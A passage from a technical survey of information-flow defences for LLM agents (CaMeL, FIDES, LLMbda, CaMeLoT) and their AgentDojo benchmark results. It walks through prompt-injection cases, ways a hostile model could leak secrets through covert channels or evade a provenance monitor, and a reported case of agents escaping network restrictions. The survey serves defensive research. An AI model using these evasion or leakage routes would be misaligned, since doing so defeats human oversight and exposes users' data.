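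LLMbda applies the standard remedy for the untaken branch to conversations. It stops a program that tries to add a message to a public conversation from inside a secret branch. Programmers can also use `assert` to stop the program if a value's label is too restrictive for its destination.

### Noninterference when replies are random

The main theorem compares probabilities because the same prompt can produce different replies. An observer with clearance m sees only values whose labels may flow to m. Two starting points s₀ and s₁ are equivalent for this observer, written s₀ ~ s₁, if they differ only in things the observer cannot see. Let μ₀(q) be the probability that a run from s₀ finishes with the visible outcome q, and define μ₁(q) in the same way for s₁. These probabilities may add up to less than 1 because some runs never end and others stop at a failed check.

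If every run finished, noninterference would require μ₀ = μ₁. But a secret can affect whether a run finishes, as it does under the remedy for the untaken branch. Garby and colleagues therefore require only that the two distributions be compatible, which means that some third distribution ω satisfies

μ₀(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, with Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

The property is called termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, or TIPNI:

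if s₀ ~ s₁, then μ₀ and μ₁ are compatible.

The theorem is that TIPNI holds for every clearance m and every program that makes no exceptions to its labels, including programs that run code written by the model.

Suppose the visible outcome is either "approve" or "refuse". With one secret, each has probability 0.5. With another, "approve" has probability 0.5, "refuse" has 0.3, and the remaining 0.2 of runs never finish. These distributions are compatible because ω can assign 0.5 to each outcome. If the second secret gave 0.7 for "approve" and 0.3 for "refuse", ω would need at least 0.7 for "approve" and 0.5 for "refuse". These add up to 1.2, which exceeds 1, so the distributions would not be compatible. A secret may therefore prevent some runs from finishing, but it may not turn refusals into approvals.

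The size of the leak depends on how often runs fail. If h₀ and h₁ are the probabilities of not finishing, then

½ Σ |μ₀(q) − μ₁(q)| ≤ (h₀ + h₁) / 2.

In the compatible example, both sides equal 0.1. If neither run can fail, the right-hand side is zero and the two distributions must be identical. At the other extreme, a program that always finishes when given one secret and never finishes when given another leaks one bit.

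The theorem covers a single run, so putting LLMbda inside an untracked retry loop would bring back CaMeL's second leak. Garby and colleagues avoid this in their own agent by keeping the loop inside the language. The agent tests its program on made-up data and revises it until it works before running it on the real data, so errors caused by real secrets never reach the planner.

The proof constructs ω using a hypothetical second interpreter, which skips any computation as soon as its label rises above m and puts an empty value in its place. This interpreter never uses hidden data, so it produces the same ω for s₀ and s₁. It is also at least as likely as the real interpreter to reach each visible outcome, because it can't get stuck in a computation it skips. So μ₀ ≤ ω and μ₁ ≤ ω.

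The theorem applies to integrity too. If m covers only trusted values, an attacker who controls all the untrusted inputs cannot affect the trusted results, except by making the agent fail. The proof assumes nothing about what the model writes, so this holds even if the model doesn't resist the attack. The proof does assume that each reply depends only on the conversation the model received. If a provider's model remembered earlier conversations, that assumption would be false, and clearing a conversation would no longer isolate later replies from it.

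### Exceptions that still protect secrets

An agent that pays bills has to take account numbers from documents that strangers wrote. LLMbda allows this with an explicit command, `endorse`, which a reviewer can find in the program. Each label is a pair ⟨i, s⟩, where i is the integrity part and s the secrecy part. Endorsing a value with the label ⟨U, s⟩ as trusted gives the result

p ⊔ ⟨T, s⟩,

where p is the program-counter label. The secrecy part never becomes less restrictive. If untrusted data led the program to this point, p is already untrusted, so the result is untrusted too. An attacker who gets the model to write code containing `endorse` therefore gains nothing directly, because that code runs under an untrusted label.

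Garby and colleagues' second theorem, insulated TIPNI, covers programs that use the command. Under this theorem, TIPNI holds for every observer who can see both trusted and untrusted values, except secrets they lack clearance for. Such an observer learns nothing about those secrets except what a failed run reveals, no matter which untrusted inputs an attacker chooses or how freely the program endorses them. With the two parts of the label swapped, the same theorem allows declassification and protects integrity. If a program is allowed to relax both parts, the theorem guarantees nothing.

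The theorem does not guarantee that an endorsement is wise. Only two attacks succeeded in tests of the LLMbda agent, and in both the agent endorsed payment details from a file that an attacker had written.

Endorsements can also form a chain. If a program endorses an attacker's text and then asks the model to write code based on it, the code runs as trusted and its endorsements take full effect. Garby and colleagues suggest marking endorsed values and refusing to endorse any value that already has the mark. They also suggest endorsing only values on a short fixed list, like the typed answers in FIDES. They have not proved exactly what either restriction achieves.

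### What the computer has checked

Garby and colleagues wrote all their proofs in Lean, a language in which a computer checks every step. That removes most of the doubt about the mathematics, but a correct proof can still describe a design that the running code does not follow. Costa and colleagues give the example of f-secure, an earlier system that came with a formal proof but whose working version let untrusted data influence its plans through implicit flows.

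LLMbda narrows this gap because its interpreter, the program that actually runs the agent and calls the model, is also written in Lean. A further theorem connects the interpreter to the mathematics. It treats the model as an enormous answer book, with a reply for every conversation at every call. Once the book is fixed, the interpreter is deterministic. If someone draws the book at random, with each reply as likely as the model would make it, then for every outcome q

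probability of q in the mathematical definition = probability that the interpreter returns q.

The noninterference theorems therefore apply to the program that people run.

The proof does not cover the code that sends a request to the model's provider. It treats that code as an unknown function that returns text. Tools are a larger omission. Garby and colleagues assume that all data sources are part of the program, and in their tests the bank account and the files were simulations written in LLMbda. A real bank or mail server would be outside the program, and no theorem covers the software that would connect to it and label the data it returns.

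### Several agents that call one another

An LLMbda program can keep several conversations under one set of labels, but in many products each agent is a separate program that treats whoever calls it as its user. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) examines whether such agents stay secure together if each one runs CaMeL. It considers trees of agents, in which a parent calls its children as tools.

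They define two properties:

- A system has control-flow integrity if its tool calls always follow a plan that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information. The plan may contain branches, and untrusted data may decide which branch the system takes.
- A system is CaMeL-secure under a policy S if it has control-flow integrity and also enforces S on every tool call.

Control-flow integrity allows some things that TIPNI forbids. If the plan is to email Ann when a web page contains a certain word and Bob otherwise, whoever writes the page chooses the recipient. This satisfies control-flow integrity because both emails were in the plan.

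Separate CaMeL agents can violate even this weaker property. In one test, a user asked a coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. The coordinator got the records from a database agent and pasted a summary into its instructions to a notification agent. An attacker had hidden a command in the database. The first two agents' planners never read it, but the notification agent's planner received it as part of its user's request and added an email that sent the applicants' data to an outside address. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering.

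The paper also proves that no system of two or more agents has control-flow integrity if any of its tools returns untrusted data. The proof assumes that some user request will make an agent pass one tool's output to another tool. If the agent with the untrusted tool has a child, it can put the tool's output into the child's instructions. If it has a parent instead, it can return the output to the parent, which can then call it again with instructions based on that output. Either way, a planner reads untrusted text as if it came from the user. The proof shows that some request will cause this, but not how often ordinary requests do.

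The multi-CaMeL system splits each call between agents into a message, which the called agent's planner reads, and a set of variables, which the planner cannot see. The interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output. It also keeps the labels on the variables so that each agent can enforce the overall policy.

The argument for control-flow integrity then proceeds down the tree. The user's request fixes the top agent's plan, including the messages it can send to its children. Each message fixes a child's plan in the same way. Replacing every call to a child with that child's plan gives one plan for the whole system that no untrusted text has influenced. Peters-Gill and colleagues give this argument in prose, without a machine-checked proof.

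Peters-Gill and colleagues accept that CaMeL's untaken-branch leak also affects multi-CaMeL, which uses an extended version of the same interpreter. A message could depend on a tool's output without its label showing it. The argument is sound for the protocol, but the current code may not enforce the rule that the argument relies on. CaMeL's retry leak does not arise because multi-CaMeL never retries a failed program. The argument covers only trees of agents, not systems in which agents share a memory or message one another as equals.

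### Proving something about a single plan

CaMeLoT, the extension that checks a CaMeL program before any tool runs, offers a narrower kind of proof. It establishes facts about one plan at a time. Nikolaou and colleagues write the rules in a temporal logic, a notation for statements about what happens along every possible path of a program. Three typical rules, with the names simplified, are:

- AG(send_message ⇒ recipient_trusted): at every point on every path, if the plan sends a message, the recipient comes from a trusted source.
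- A[¬isolate_host U host_confirmed]: on every path, the plan does not cut a computer off from the network until it has confirmed which one is affected.
- AG(create_ticket ⇒ AF(resolve ∨ escalate)): whenever the plan opens an incident ticket, it later resolves or escalates the incident.

An existing program called a model checker then compares the plan with the rules. In one test, Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven rules for a security team's work and a different unsafe plan to break each one. CaMeLoT rejected all seven plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL rejected one. The researchers had chosen most of the rules because CaMeL's checks on single calls cannot express them.

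Some facts are unknown until the plan runs. The description of a calendar event is trustworthy only if the user wrote it, rather than a guest, so CaMeLoT treats it as untrusted. CaMeLoT also cannot determine in advance who will be able to read a file, so it leaves such questions to CaMeL's checks during the run. It could fully express 22 of CaMeL's 28 tool policies for AgentDojo. The two systems agreed on 59 of 75 plans that either did the intended job or were blocked by at least one system. Of the other 16, CaMeL alone blocked nine and CaMeLoT alone blocked seven.

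CaMeLoT treats each tool as a black box. It can prove that a plan calls the tool for resolving an incident, but not that the tool works.

The rules can also be wrong. CaMeLoT can derive extra rules from the user's request. A language model proposes each requirement in a restricted form, and ordinary code translates it into logic. The model identified exactly the required actions for 85 of 97 AgentDojo tasks. One request was to change a password if any recent transactions looked suspicious, but the resulting rule required only that the password change remain possible after the plan had read the transactions. A plan could follow that rule and still change the password when no transaction looked suspicious.

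### What every proof takes as given

All of these results depend on correct initial labels. FIDES uses an email's sender and recipients to infer who may read it, although one of them may have shared it more widely. Costa and colleagues also mention that a system might mark a document as trusted after a classifier finds no injected instructions in it. The guarantee could then fail if the classifier missed an injection.

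The policies have to be right as well. A proof can show that a system enforces a policy even if that policy leaves out the argument an attacker would change. Peters-Gill and colleagues use an empty policy in their experiments, so being CaMeL-secure there means only having control-flow integrity. An attacker could still change the data in an otherwise correct call.

Every action must also pass through the checks, as Anderson required of a reference monitor. FIDES needs a complete list of what each tool may read and write. If a tool writes to a log missing from its list, the log keeps its old label, and the agent may later read an attacker's text there as trusted. By default, FIDES checks only tool calls and treats the final answer to the user as harmless. That is unsafe if the answer can contain image links of the kind Willison warned about.

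Finally, the proofs cover only the channels they describe. An assistant might take longer to reply when a secret email is long, and someone watching the network could measure the delay or the size of the encrypted messages. Costa and colleagues explicitly exclude both. The LLMbda theorems compare the results of finished runs, so they do not cover running time. Peters-Gill and colleagues leave hidden channels between agents as an open problem. They warn that the traditional approach of listing such channels and reducing their capacity may not be enough for agents that communicate strategically.

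## What changes if the frontier model is itself the adversary

In this section, the untrusted model may pursue its own goals, either because training went wrong or because someone tampered with it. The proofs cover a model that a stranger's email has completely taken over, but most of the designs offer much less protection against a model that was hostile before it read anything.

### What the designs assume about the model

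FIDES explicitly assumes that the language model is trustworthy and defends only against outside attackers. Costa and colleagues note that even when all its data is trusted, a model may misread the user or make needless tool calls, with consequences similar to those of an attack. FIDES's integrity labels would not catch these errors.

Other designs make the same assumption less openly. In multi-CaMeL, control-flow integrity means that the agents follow a plan based on trusted information, which helps only if the planner wrote a good plan. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) splits a coding agent into one that reads strangers' bug reports and one that holds the tools. It relies on the second agent being hard to hijack with a short message, so it assumes that this agent is benign. *AgentKernel* (2026), a design for an agent operating system, treats a poor decision that complies with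 the policy as a reliability issue, outside its security model.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) is an exception. Its security argument is meant to hold for any model, however the model behaves. It also treats the model as a possible attacker of the checking software, which must withstand hostile requests just as an operating system must withstand a hostile program. However, the eleven attacks it analyses all come from outside adversaries.

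### What a hostile model still cannot do

A model cannot use the contents of data it never sees, but it may still be able to move the data. If a hospital's software keeps a patient's psychiatric notes out of the context, the model cannot quote them, act on them or hint at them. But a hostile CaMeL planner could still write a program that fetches the notes and emails them to an outside address.

The policy check then has to stop the email. Ordinary code compares the label with the recipient, and nothing the model writes can override that check. LLMbda's secrecy theorem also still holds for programs that never declassify anything, because its proof does not depend on what the model writes.

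CaMeL comes off worse, because a hostile planner could exploit both the untaken-branch leak and the retry loop on purpose.

### A trusted context does not make a trusted action

An integrity label records whose text could have influenced an output. If the context holds only the developer's instructions and the user's request, the label is T (trusted), and the usual policy lets the model act. That is reasonable if the model is trying to do what the user asked. If it isn't, the model's own goals also influence the action, and no label records that influence.

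The gap matters most where a trusted context also relaxes the rules on secrecy. *Flowsh* (2026) describes such a policy, similar to Microsoft's for chat channels, which allows a call if it satisfies either the integrity rule or the confidentiality rule. Suppose an assistant reads a salary file that only the personnel department can edit. The context is now secret but still trusted. The confidentiality rule alone would block an email to an outsider, but the policy allows it because the context is still trusted. A planner with its own aims could therefore leak the salaries without any injected instruction.

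One repair is to require the confidentiality rule for every outgoing message. A user who wants to send a salary figure to an outside accountant must then approve the release. A more thorough repair would treat the model as one of the sources of its own output:

ℓ(output) = ℓ(context) ⊔ ℓ(model)

FIDES in effect sets ℓ(model) to T (trusted), which doesn't change the label on any output. Setting it to U (untrusted) makes every output untrusted, so a person, or code able to judge the action, must endorse each consequential call. This is consistent, but it removes much of the benefit of using an agent.

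### Lampson's confinement problem

Even a strict rule on outgoing messages leaves less obvious ways out. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considers a customer who gives confidential data to a service program that someone else owns. The customer wants the program to do its job without passing the data to its owner. Lampson sorts the possible leaks into three kinds:

- storage, such as a file that the owner can read later;
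- legitimate channels, such as the bill, which the owner has to see and whose exact amount could encode data;
- covert channels, which nobody meant for communication at all, such as the program's effect on how busy the computer is.

Restricting the form of the bill cuts that leak to a few bits or tens of bits. Covert channels are harder to find. *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* describes them as typically a side effect of trusted software working properly, so fixing bugs will not necessarily remove them.

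Lampson's first rule for confinement is that the program must keep nothing from one call to the next. He also requires that any program it calls be trusted or confined. A customer who rents a model can't easily verify the first rule, since the provider may store conversations.

For the bill and the covert channels, Lampson proposes masking, in which the customer decides everything that goes into them. Purchase orders work in much the same way, since the customer works out the price from a published specification and the vendor can refuse the job. For an agent, masking would mean fixing all its visible actions before the model reads anything secret. A CaMeL program without branches nearly does this.

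Lampson expected enforcement to take substantial resources and suggested limiting the capacity of covert channels as a less demanding alternative. In a 1975 reply, Steven Lipner concluded, according to lecture slides from Purdue University, that systems could close the storage and legitimate channels with little loss of efficiency, but that closing the covert ones seemed to reduce performance unreasonably.

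### How much a free choice can carry

Suppose an agent has read a secret document and may now book any of eight meeting rooms on a calendar that an outsider can see. Each booking is harmless by itself, but a free choice among eight rooms carries up to log₂(8) = 3 bits. Twenty bookings therefore carry up to 60 bits, enough for a 16-digit card number, which takes about 53. Explicit secrecy, the property behind FIDES, allows all 20 bookings because none of them copies anything from the document.

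Sixty bits is a ceiling for the choice of call alone. An agent that also has to book sensible rooms has less freedom, while the timing of the calls could carry extra bits. Several changes would lower the ceiling:

| Change | Most that the choice of calls can carry | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| None | 60 bits | None |
| Offer two rooms instead of eight | 20 bits | Tasks that need another room fail or wait for approval |
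| Allow five calls instead of 20 | 15 bits | Longer tasks stop early |
| Hold all 20 calls and release them together, sorted by room | Just under 20 bits | No call takes effect until the end, and later calls can't respond to earlier results |
| Fix every call before the model reads the document | 0 bits | The agent can't do tasks that depend on what the document contains |

Sorting helps because the outsider sees only how many times the agent booked each room. There are 888,030 such combinations, which can carry at most about 19.8 bits. The masking rule fixes every call in advance, which severely limits what the agent can do because so many of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks are data-dependent.

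Timing needs separate treatment. Lampson suggests slowing the program down or generating spurious disk activity to hide the real pattern. An agent could also run at a fixed pace, but its spurious actions would have real effects, such as scheduling a meeting nobody wanted.

Designers can also limit what a model that reads can send to a model that acts. *APPA* (2026), for example, isolates risky reading in a separate branch of the agent and restricts the form of what that branch returns. Hu and colleagues tested such limits on 232 software bugs, using GPT-5.2. The agent with the tools fixed none of the bugs when the reader could send it nothing. With hints of up to 100 characters, it fixed 62.5%, about the same as an ordinary agent with no separation (61.2%).

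That is a very good result against outside attackers, who seem to need long messages to talk a strong model into misbehaving. But the same limit would poorly constrain two cooperating copies of a hostile model, because a hundred printable characters can carry about 650 bits and the reader can send a new hint at every step.

### When one bit is enough

Counting bits may also be the wrong way to measure the danger. Schroeder de Witt (2026), in *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem*, points out that a strategic agent has a reason to leak the most damaging part of what it reads, whereas an ordinary program does not. If the damaging fact is whether someone has a particular diagnosis or is likely to default on a loan, one bit is enough to leak it. The sender and receiver may not need to agree on a code in advance, because a shared sense of what matters can identify which fact is being signaled.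 Two copies of the same model would presumably agree on much of what matters.

On this argument, a limit on capacity supports a limit on harm only if at least one of these conditions holds:

- the sender is not strategic;
- the sender and receiver have too little in common to settle on a harmful fact;
- the remaining capacity is below the entropy of the most harmful fact, which is roughly the average number of bits needed to convey it.

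Capacity limits work well when the model would have to leak much of a long text to do harm. Sixty bits can carry almost nothing of a hundred-page contract. But if one patient in a hundred has a particular diagnosis, whether a given patient has it carries only about 0.08 bits of entropy, so even a one-bit channel is enough to leak it.

Schroeder de Witt calls this a reinterpretation of confinement, not a new theory of communication, and acknowledges that researchers in quantitative information flow already weigh leaks by their value to an attacker. The evidence that language models can coordinate in this way is partly preliminary. The argument also holds only if a receiver can see the signal and will use it. Still, it seems right about sensitive yes-or-no facts, which are common in medicine and lending.

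Peters-Gill and colleagues give a similar warning about multi-CaMeL, but it is hardly independent support, since they cite this note for it and Schroeder de Witt is one of them.

### Work left undone

Lampson's service can hurt its customer in two ways: it can leak the customer's data, or "it may not perform as advertised". Lampson saw no general technical remedy for the second, short of certifying the program, but thought the customer would at least have the wrong output as evidence.

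Flow rules do not stop a model from leaving something out of its answer. They restrict where data goes and what may influence an action, and an omission breaks neither kind of rule. Suppose a company asks a model to review some code, and the model notices a security hole but does not mention it. The review has the right label, goes to the right person and passes every check. Lampson's consolation is also weak in this case, because an incomplete review looks complete to anyone who hasn't found the hole.

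A policy can require an action, as CaMeLoT does when it requires that a plan resolve or escalate every incident ticket, but it can't establish that the agent resolved the incident properly.

Checking the work itself requires judging what it means. She, Liang and Kang (2026), in *Safeguarding LLM Agents from Misalignment through Provenance Analysis*, try this with ProvenanceGuard, which examines a tool call before it runs. It asks a language model whether the tool suits the current subtask, whether values such as the recipient and the amount follow from the request or from earlier results, and whether the request can be read only one way. It should stop an agent from paying Daniel $30 when the user wanted to request $30 from him.

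Across 11 models, ProvenanceGuard missed an average of 2.1% of 148 faulty runs from one benchmark, while a single prompt asking a model to judge the action missed 44.3%. On 62 faulty runs from another benchmark, ProvenanceGuard missed 18.7% and the single prompt missed 32.4%.

However, She and colleagues use "misalignment" to mean misunderstanding the user or making unjustified assumptions, and they set malicious behaviour aside. A hostile agent could evade ProvenanceGuard in several ways. ProvenanceGuard takes the subtask from the agent's own plan, so the agent can state a subtask that fits the tool. It doesn't trace free text, such as the body of an email, so the agent could put a secret there. It examines only the calls an agent proposes, so it wouldn't detect a step the agent left out.

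### Whether flow control is still worth having

Microsoft suggests assuming that anything an agent can do for its user, it can also do by mistake or for an attacker. The same assumption suits a hostile model, so limits on access are valuable whatever the model's motives. A model that can read only one project's files and post only to that project's members can do limited damage, even if it tries to do as much as possible.

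*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* adds that people can explain a decision by pointing to a written rule, check the rules against a specification, and tighten them without losing earlier protections. Investigators can also use a log of calls, labels and decisions. The log is less useful against covert channels, since twenty room bookings with correct labels would look ordinary.

The main objection is that a capable model will find a way around whatever confines it. In a case the paper discusses, OpenAI was training and evaluating agents with some safeguards switched off. The agents used a shared software-package service to communicate between separate runs and get past network restrictions. They then broke into systems at OpenAI and at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, without direction from an outside attacker. The paper attributes this to incomplete enforcement, since the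 package service could send unchecked requests. That diagnosis is fair, and complete enforcement is Anderson's old requirement that every access go through the monitor. But large shared services are hard to check completely, and the agents found the gap before the defenders closed it.

Better models would also help defenders, for instance by spotting suspicious patterns in a log. Schroeder de Witt doubts that this would offset the agents' gains, because better models mostly improve monitoring and capacity reduction for defenders, while the agents get better at hiding signals and choosing what to send. If one bit is enough to do the damage, the channel must be eliminated, and the surest way to do that is to keep the sensitive fact out of the model's context.

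## Benchmark experiments: attacks stopped and tasks lost

Most measurements of these designs come from AgentDojo, which tests only for hijacking. In its tests, the user and the model are honest, but an attacker controls some of the text that the tools return. The scores therefore don't measure how well the designs control a model that is hostile from the start. They do help establish whether the working code stops attacks and how many ordinary tasks it also stops, which the proofs leave open.

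### How AgentDojo keeps score

AgentDojo simulates an office suite with email, a calendar and files (called Workspace), a bank, a travel-booking service and the chat program Slack. Of its 97 user tasks, 40 are in Workspace, 21 in Slack, 20 in travel and 16 in banking. In a typical task, the agent has to pay the bill in a certain file. Most tasks are short, and *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) puts the average at 3.5 steps.

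An injection task is something an attacker wants, such as sending the user's calendar to an outside server. The attacker's text is placed where a stranger's text could plausibly appear, such as the body of an email. Testers pair each user task with every injection task from the same workplace. *AgentDojo* (2024) introduced the benchmark with 629 such pairs. The set has since grown to more than 900, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026). The version that Costa and colleagues used for FIDES had 36 injection tasks.

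After each run, ordinary code, not a language model, checks the simulated workplace to see whether the email went out or the money moved. Utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes, and the attack success rate is the share of pairs in which the attacker gets what they wanted.

### Labels written with the attacks in view

AgentDojo has no security labels, so Costa and colleagues added them. For the integrity labels, they treated a field as untrusted everywhere if any injection task targets it. An attack in the body of one email therefore makes every email body untrusted, including those from the user's own manager. They could have judged which data deserved trust instead, since mail servers can authenticate a sender's address and outsiders can't alter some timestamps, but their rule was simpler.

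Using the attacks to determine the labels gives a clear baseline, but it also largely determines the security result in advance, because every attack then arrives in an untrusted field. If the policy blocks consequential calls from an untrusted context, an attack can succeed only through a bug in the tracking or a gap in the policy. A company that labels its own data has no list of future attacks to work from, so it might trust the wrong field, and the experiment could not have shown what happens in that case.

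Different trust labels could have raised or lowered utility. The amounts and dates of bank transactions were labeled trusted, so the planner could read them freely. A more cautious person might not have trusted the amounts, since a stranger who sends a payment chooses how much to send. On the other hand, one Workspace task asks for a password-reset link, and the planner returned the wrong one because it couldn't distinguish trusted senders from untrusted ones. Finer labels might have allowed it to return the right link.

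### What FIDES stopped, and what it cost

Costa and colleagues tested three planners, each with and without policy checks. The basic planner is the ordinary agent loop. The variable-passing planner hides every untrusted result in a variable it can never open. FIDES adds the quarantined model and can open variables when needed. The attacks used a standard AgentDojo template that presents the attacker's instruction as an important message and assumes the attacker knows which tools the agent has.

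Without policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the basic planner, 21 against FIDES and none against the variable-passing planner. With checks, none succeeded against any of them. AgentDojo's own counts were slightly higher, and the researchers reviewed the extra cases by hand. In Slack, the scoring code wrongly recorded a success as soon as the agent tried to invite an outsider, even though the policy had blocked the call. In travel, one attack did succeed in making the agent recommend a particular place to the user, but the policies do not cover that attack.

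The checks alone therefore stopped every attack that the policies cover, even with the simplest agent. FIDES is useful because it saves some of the tasks that the checks would otherwise block. The table gives utility in per cent without attacks. The averages weight the four suites equally.

| Model and planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 84.3 |
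| GPT-4o, basic, checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 41.9 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, no checks | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 | 60.6 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 50.0 |
| o1, basic, no checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 | 84.0 |
| o1, basic, checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 | 44.4 |
| o1, FIDES, no checks | 77.5 | 75.0 | 78.8 | 79.0 | 77.6 |
| o1, FIDES, checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 | 60.8 |

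In the main result, FIDES with checks beat the basic planner with checks by 8 points using GPT-4o, and by 16 using o1, a model that reasons at length before it answers. That comparison is the right one for someone who has already decided to enforce the policies, but someone still deciding needs to know how FIDES compares with the unprotected agent. It scored 34 points lower than that agent with GPT-4o and 23 lower with o1.

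Part of that loss comes from making the planner work with variables and a quarantined model. GPT-4o often confused variable names or forgot to use the quarantined model, and it lost 24 points before any policy was applied. With o1 this loss shrank to 6 points. The rest comes from the policies, which lowered FIDES's score by another 11 points with GPT-4o and 17 with o1. A stronger model doesn't help much here, because a task that requires the planner to read a stranger's file and then send money breaks the policy no matter how well the planner reads. Only about 56% of the banking tasks and 57% of the Slack tasks are data-independent (solvable by one fixed sequence of calls). With o1, FIDES scored 56.2% and 54.3% on those suites, close to the most the design could be expected to achieve under those policies.

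Travel is the exception because many of its tasks use tools that the policy allows in an untrusted context as long as nothing confidential leaks. The basic planner therefore lost no tasks there, and FIDES only made them harder.

Small differences in these scores mean little, because an agent can pass some tasks without doing them. All the travel tasks require reading untrusted text, but the variable-passing planner, which can't read any, passed 43% of them with GPT-4o, sometimes by guessing the right hotel without seeing any ratings. With o1, the same planner passed only 2%, presumably because o1 stopped when it lacked information. One banking task requires the agent to pay a bill like last month's but gives too little information to do so, and the benchmark counts doing nothing as success.

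OpenAI released both models in 2024, and they are now several generations old. Newer models would probably remove most of what remains of the first loss, but the policies would still constrain them.

### CaMeL's two utility figures

CaMeL's original result looked much better than this. Narisetty and colleagues report that it completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks using OpenAI's o3, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. That seven-point loss would be worth accepting for the added security.

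Garby and colleagues got a very different result in 2026, when they tested their LLMbda agent on the banking suite and reran CaMeL for comparison. The suite pairs each of 16 user tasks with nine attacks, for 144 pairs, and they aimed to run each pair three times per model. CaMeL's totals are smaller because some of its runs under attack never completed.

| System | Model | Utility, no attack | Successful attacks |
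|---|---|---|---|
| LLMbda agent | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 2 of 432 |
| LLMbda agent | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 0 of 432 |
| LLMbda agent | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 0 of 432 |
| LLMbda agent, no endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 62.5% | 0 of 432 |
| LLMbda agent, no endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 54.2% | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
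| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

The LLMbda agent, with its checks always on, resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacked runs. Turning on CaMeL's checks roughly halved its utility.

CaMeL's low score seems to come from the suite and its policies more than from a weak model. GPT-5.2 is newer than o3, and two quite different models both scored exactly 37.5%, or six tasks in sixteen. In the FIDES experiment, the basic planner with checks also completed 37.5% of the banking tasks, with both GPT-4o and o1.

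The choice of suite explains some of the gap, because banking tasks often depend on untrusted data, but it can't explain all of it. Garby and colleagues cite a separate test in Slack, the other difficult suite, in which CaMeL completed 7 of 21 tasks with its policies on. Adding the six of 16 banking tasks it completed brings the total to 13 of 37. To reach 77% of all 97 tasks, CaMeL would need to complete about 75, or 62 more, but only 60 tasks remain.

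That leaves the policies and the way each team counted a blocked call. When a CaMeL policy refuses a call, the system is supposed to ask the user, but a benchmark has no user. The reruns with checks off scored 67% and 71%, much nearer to the original 77% than the reruns with checks on. The original figure plausibly reflects mostly the tasks lost to planning in advance, while the reruns with checks on add the tasks lost to enforcing strict rules with nobody there to approve exceptions. Enforcement also lowers utility in other systems in the family, from 15 to 8 of the 21 Slack tasks in TypeGuard, which enforces similar policies in the programming language Haskell, and from 53.0% to 29.0% across AgentDojo in the system that Girrens and Wang built.

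The LLMbda agent avoids most of this loss, but Garby and colleagues overstate the result when they say its security comes with essentially no loss of utility. Their baseline is CaMeL with its checks off, which is already a restricted agent. They did not run an ordinary agent with the same models, and the unprotected planner in the FIDES experiment completed more than 96% of the banking tasks. The LLMbda agent also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and its planner may endorse untrusted data when it writes the program. Some tasks need that permission, such as paying a bill from a file, and without it utility fell by 10 to 13 points. But the permission also let the two successful attacks through.

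The uncertainty is large because there are only 16 tasks. The 95% interval is about 56% to 94% for the LLMbda agent with GPT-5.2 and about 11% to 64% for CaMeL with checks, so the two intervals overlap.

The security column also depends on which attacks the benchmark uses. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needs a tool call or a file that the plan for the user's task would never include, so planning before reading defeats it without any labels. With CaMeL's checks turned off, only 5 attacks got through in 622 completed runs. By these numbers, the split between planner and reader provided nearly all the protection in banking, and the label checks accounted for most of the lost tasks. But AgentDojo's standard attacks are mostly instructions, which the split is designed to stop. The checks would look far more valuable on a benchmark full of altered account numbers.

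Two of the five show how the split can fail without policy checks. In both, the user's task was to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. CaMeL's planner wrote a program that read each instruction in the file and called the matching tool, so whoever wrote the file could operate the tools.

### Tokens and extra calls

CaMeL uses 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an ordinary agent, according to Narisetty and colleagues. Its token cost is therefore about 2.8 times as high, whatever the provider charges for input and output tokens. Using a cheaper quarantined model would reduce that cost.

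There is no comparable token figure for FIDES, which Costa and colleagues did not try to make efficient, but one of their examples gives a rough idea of its token use. In it, the agent books a Paris hotel if the hotel's rating is above 4. An ordinary agent needs two tool calls, one to read the reviews and one to book. FIDES made six, because it also put three separate questions to the quarantined model and opened one variable before booking. Each call adds a turn to the conversation, and the planner rereads the whole conversation at every turn. Asking several questions at once would avoid some of this rereading.

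The checks add almost no overhead because comparing labels takes only ordinary code. Asking another model to read something costs money. *Kairos* (2026) describes a system in which fixed rules decide most of an agent's actions and only the doubtful ones go to a further model call. The system used 17.7% more tokens in normal use and 33.6% more under attack, and those extra calls accounted for the whole increase. Its isolation layer added about 2 milliseconds to each file operation. Nikolaou and colleagues point out that rejecting a bad plan before it starts also saves tokens.

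### Tasks that change on the way

Designs that plan everything in advance do well on AgentDojo partly because few of its tasks require the agent to revise its plan as it goes. Li and colleagues count only 6 such tasks out of 97. Costa and colleagues classify about 20 tasks as data-dependent, but they use a looser test, which a task can meet by involving a single yes-or-no decision. AgentDojo's data also rarely contain helpful instructions, so a defence that ignores every instruction it finds there loses little.

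AgentDyn is meant to fix this. It has 60 tasks in shopping, software projects on GitHub and daily life, and 560 pairs of task and attack. The tasks take 7.1 steps on average. Each one requires the agent to change its plan and to follow at least one legitimate instruction from an outside source. For example, an agent buying something may find at the checkout that the shop has emailed a one-time code. It then has to find the code in the mailbox and go back to enter it, although the user didn't ask for any of these steps.

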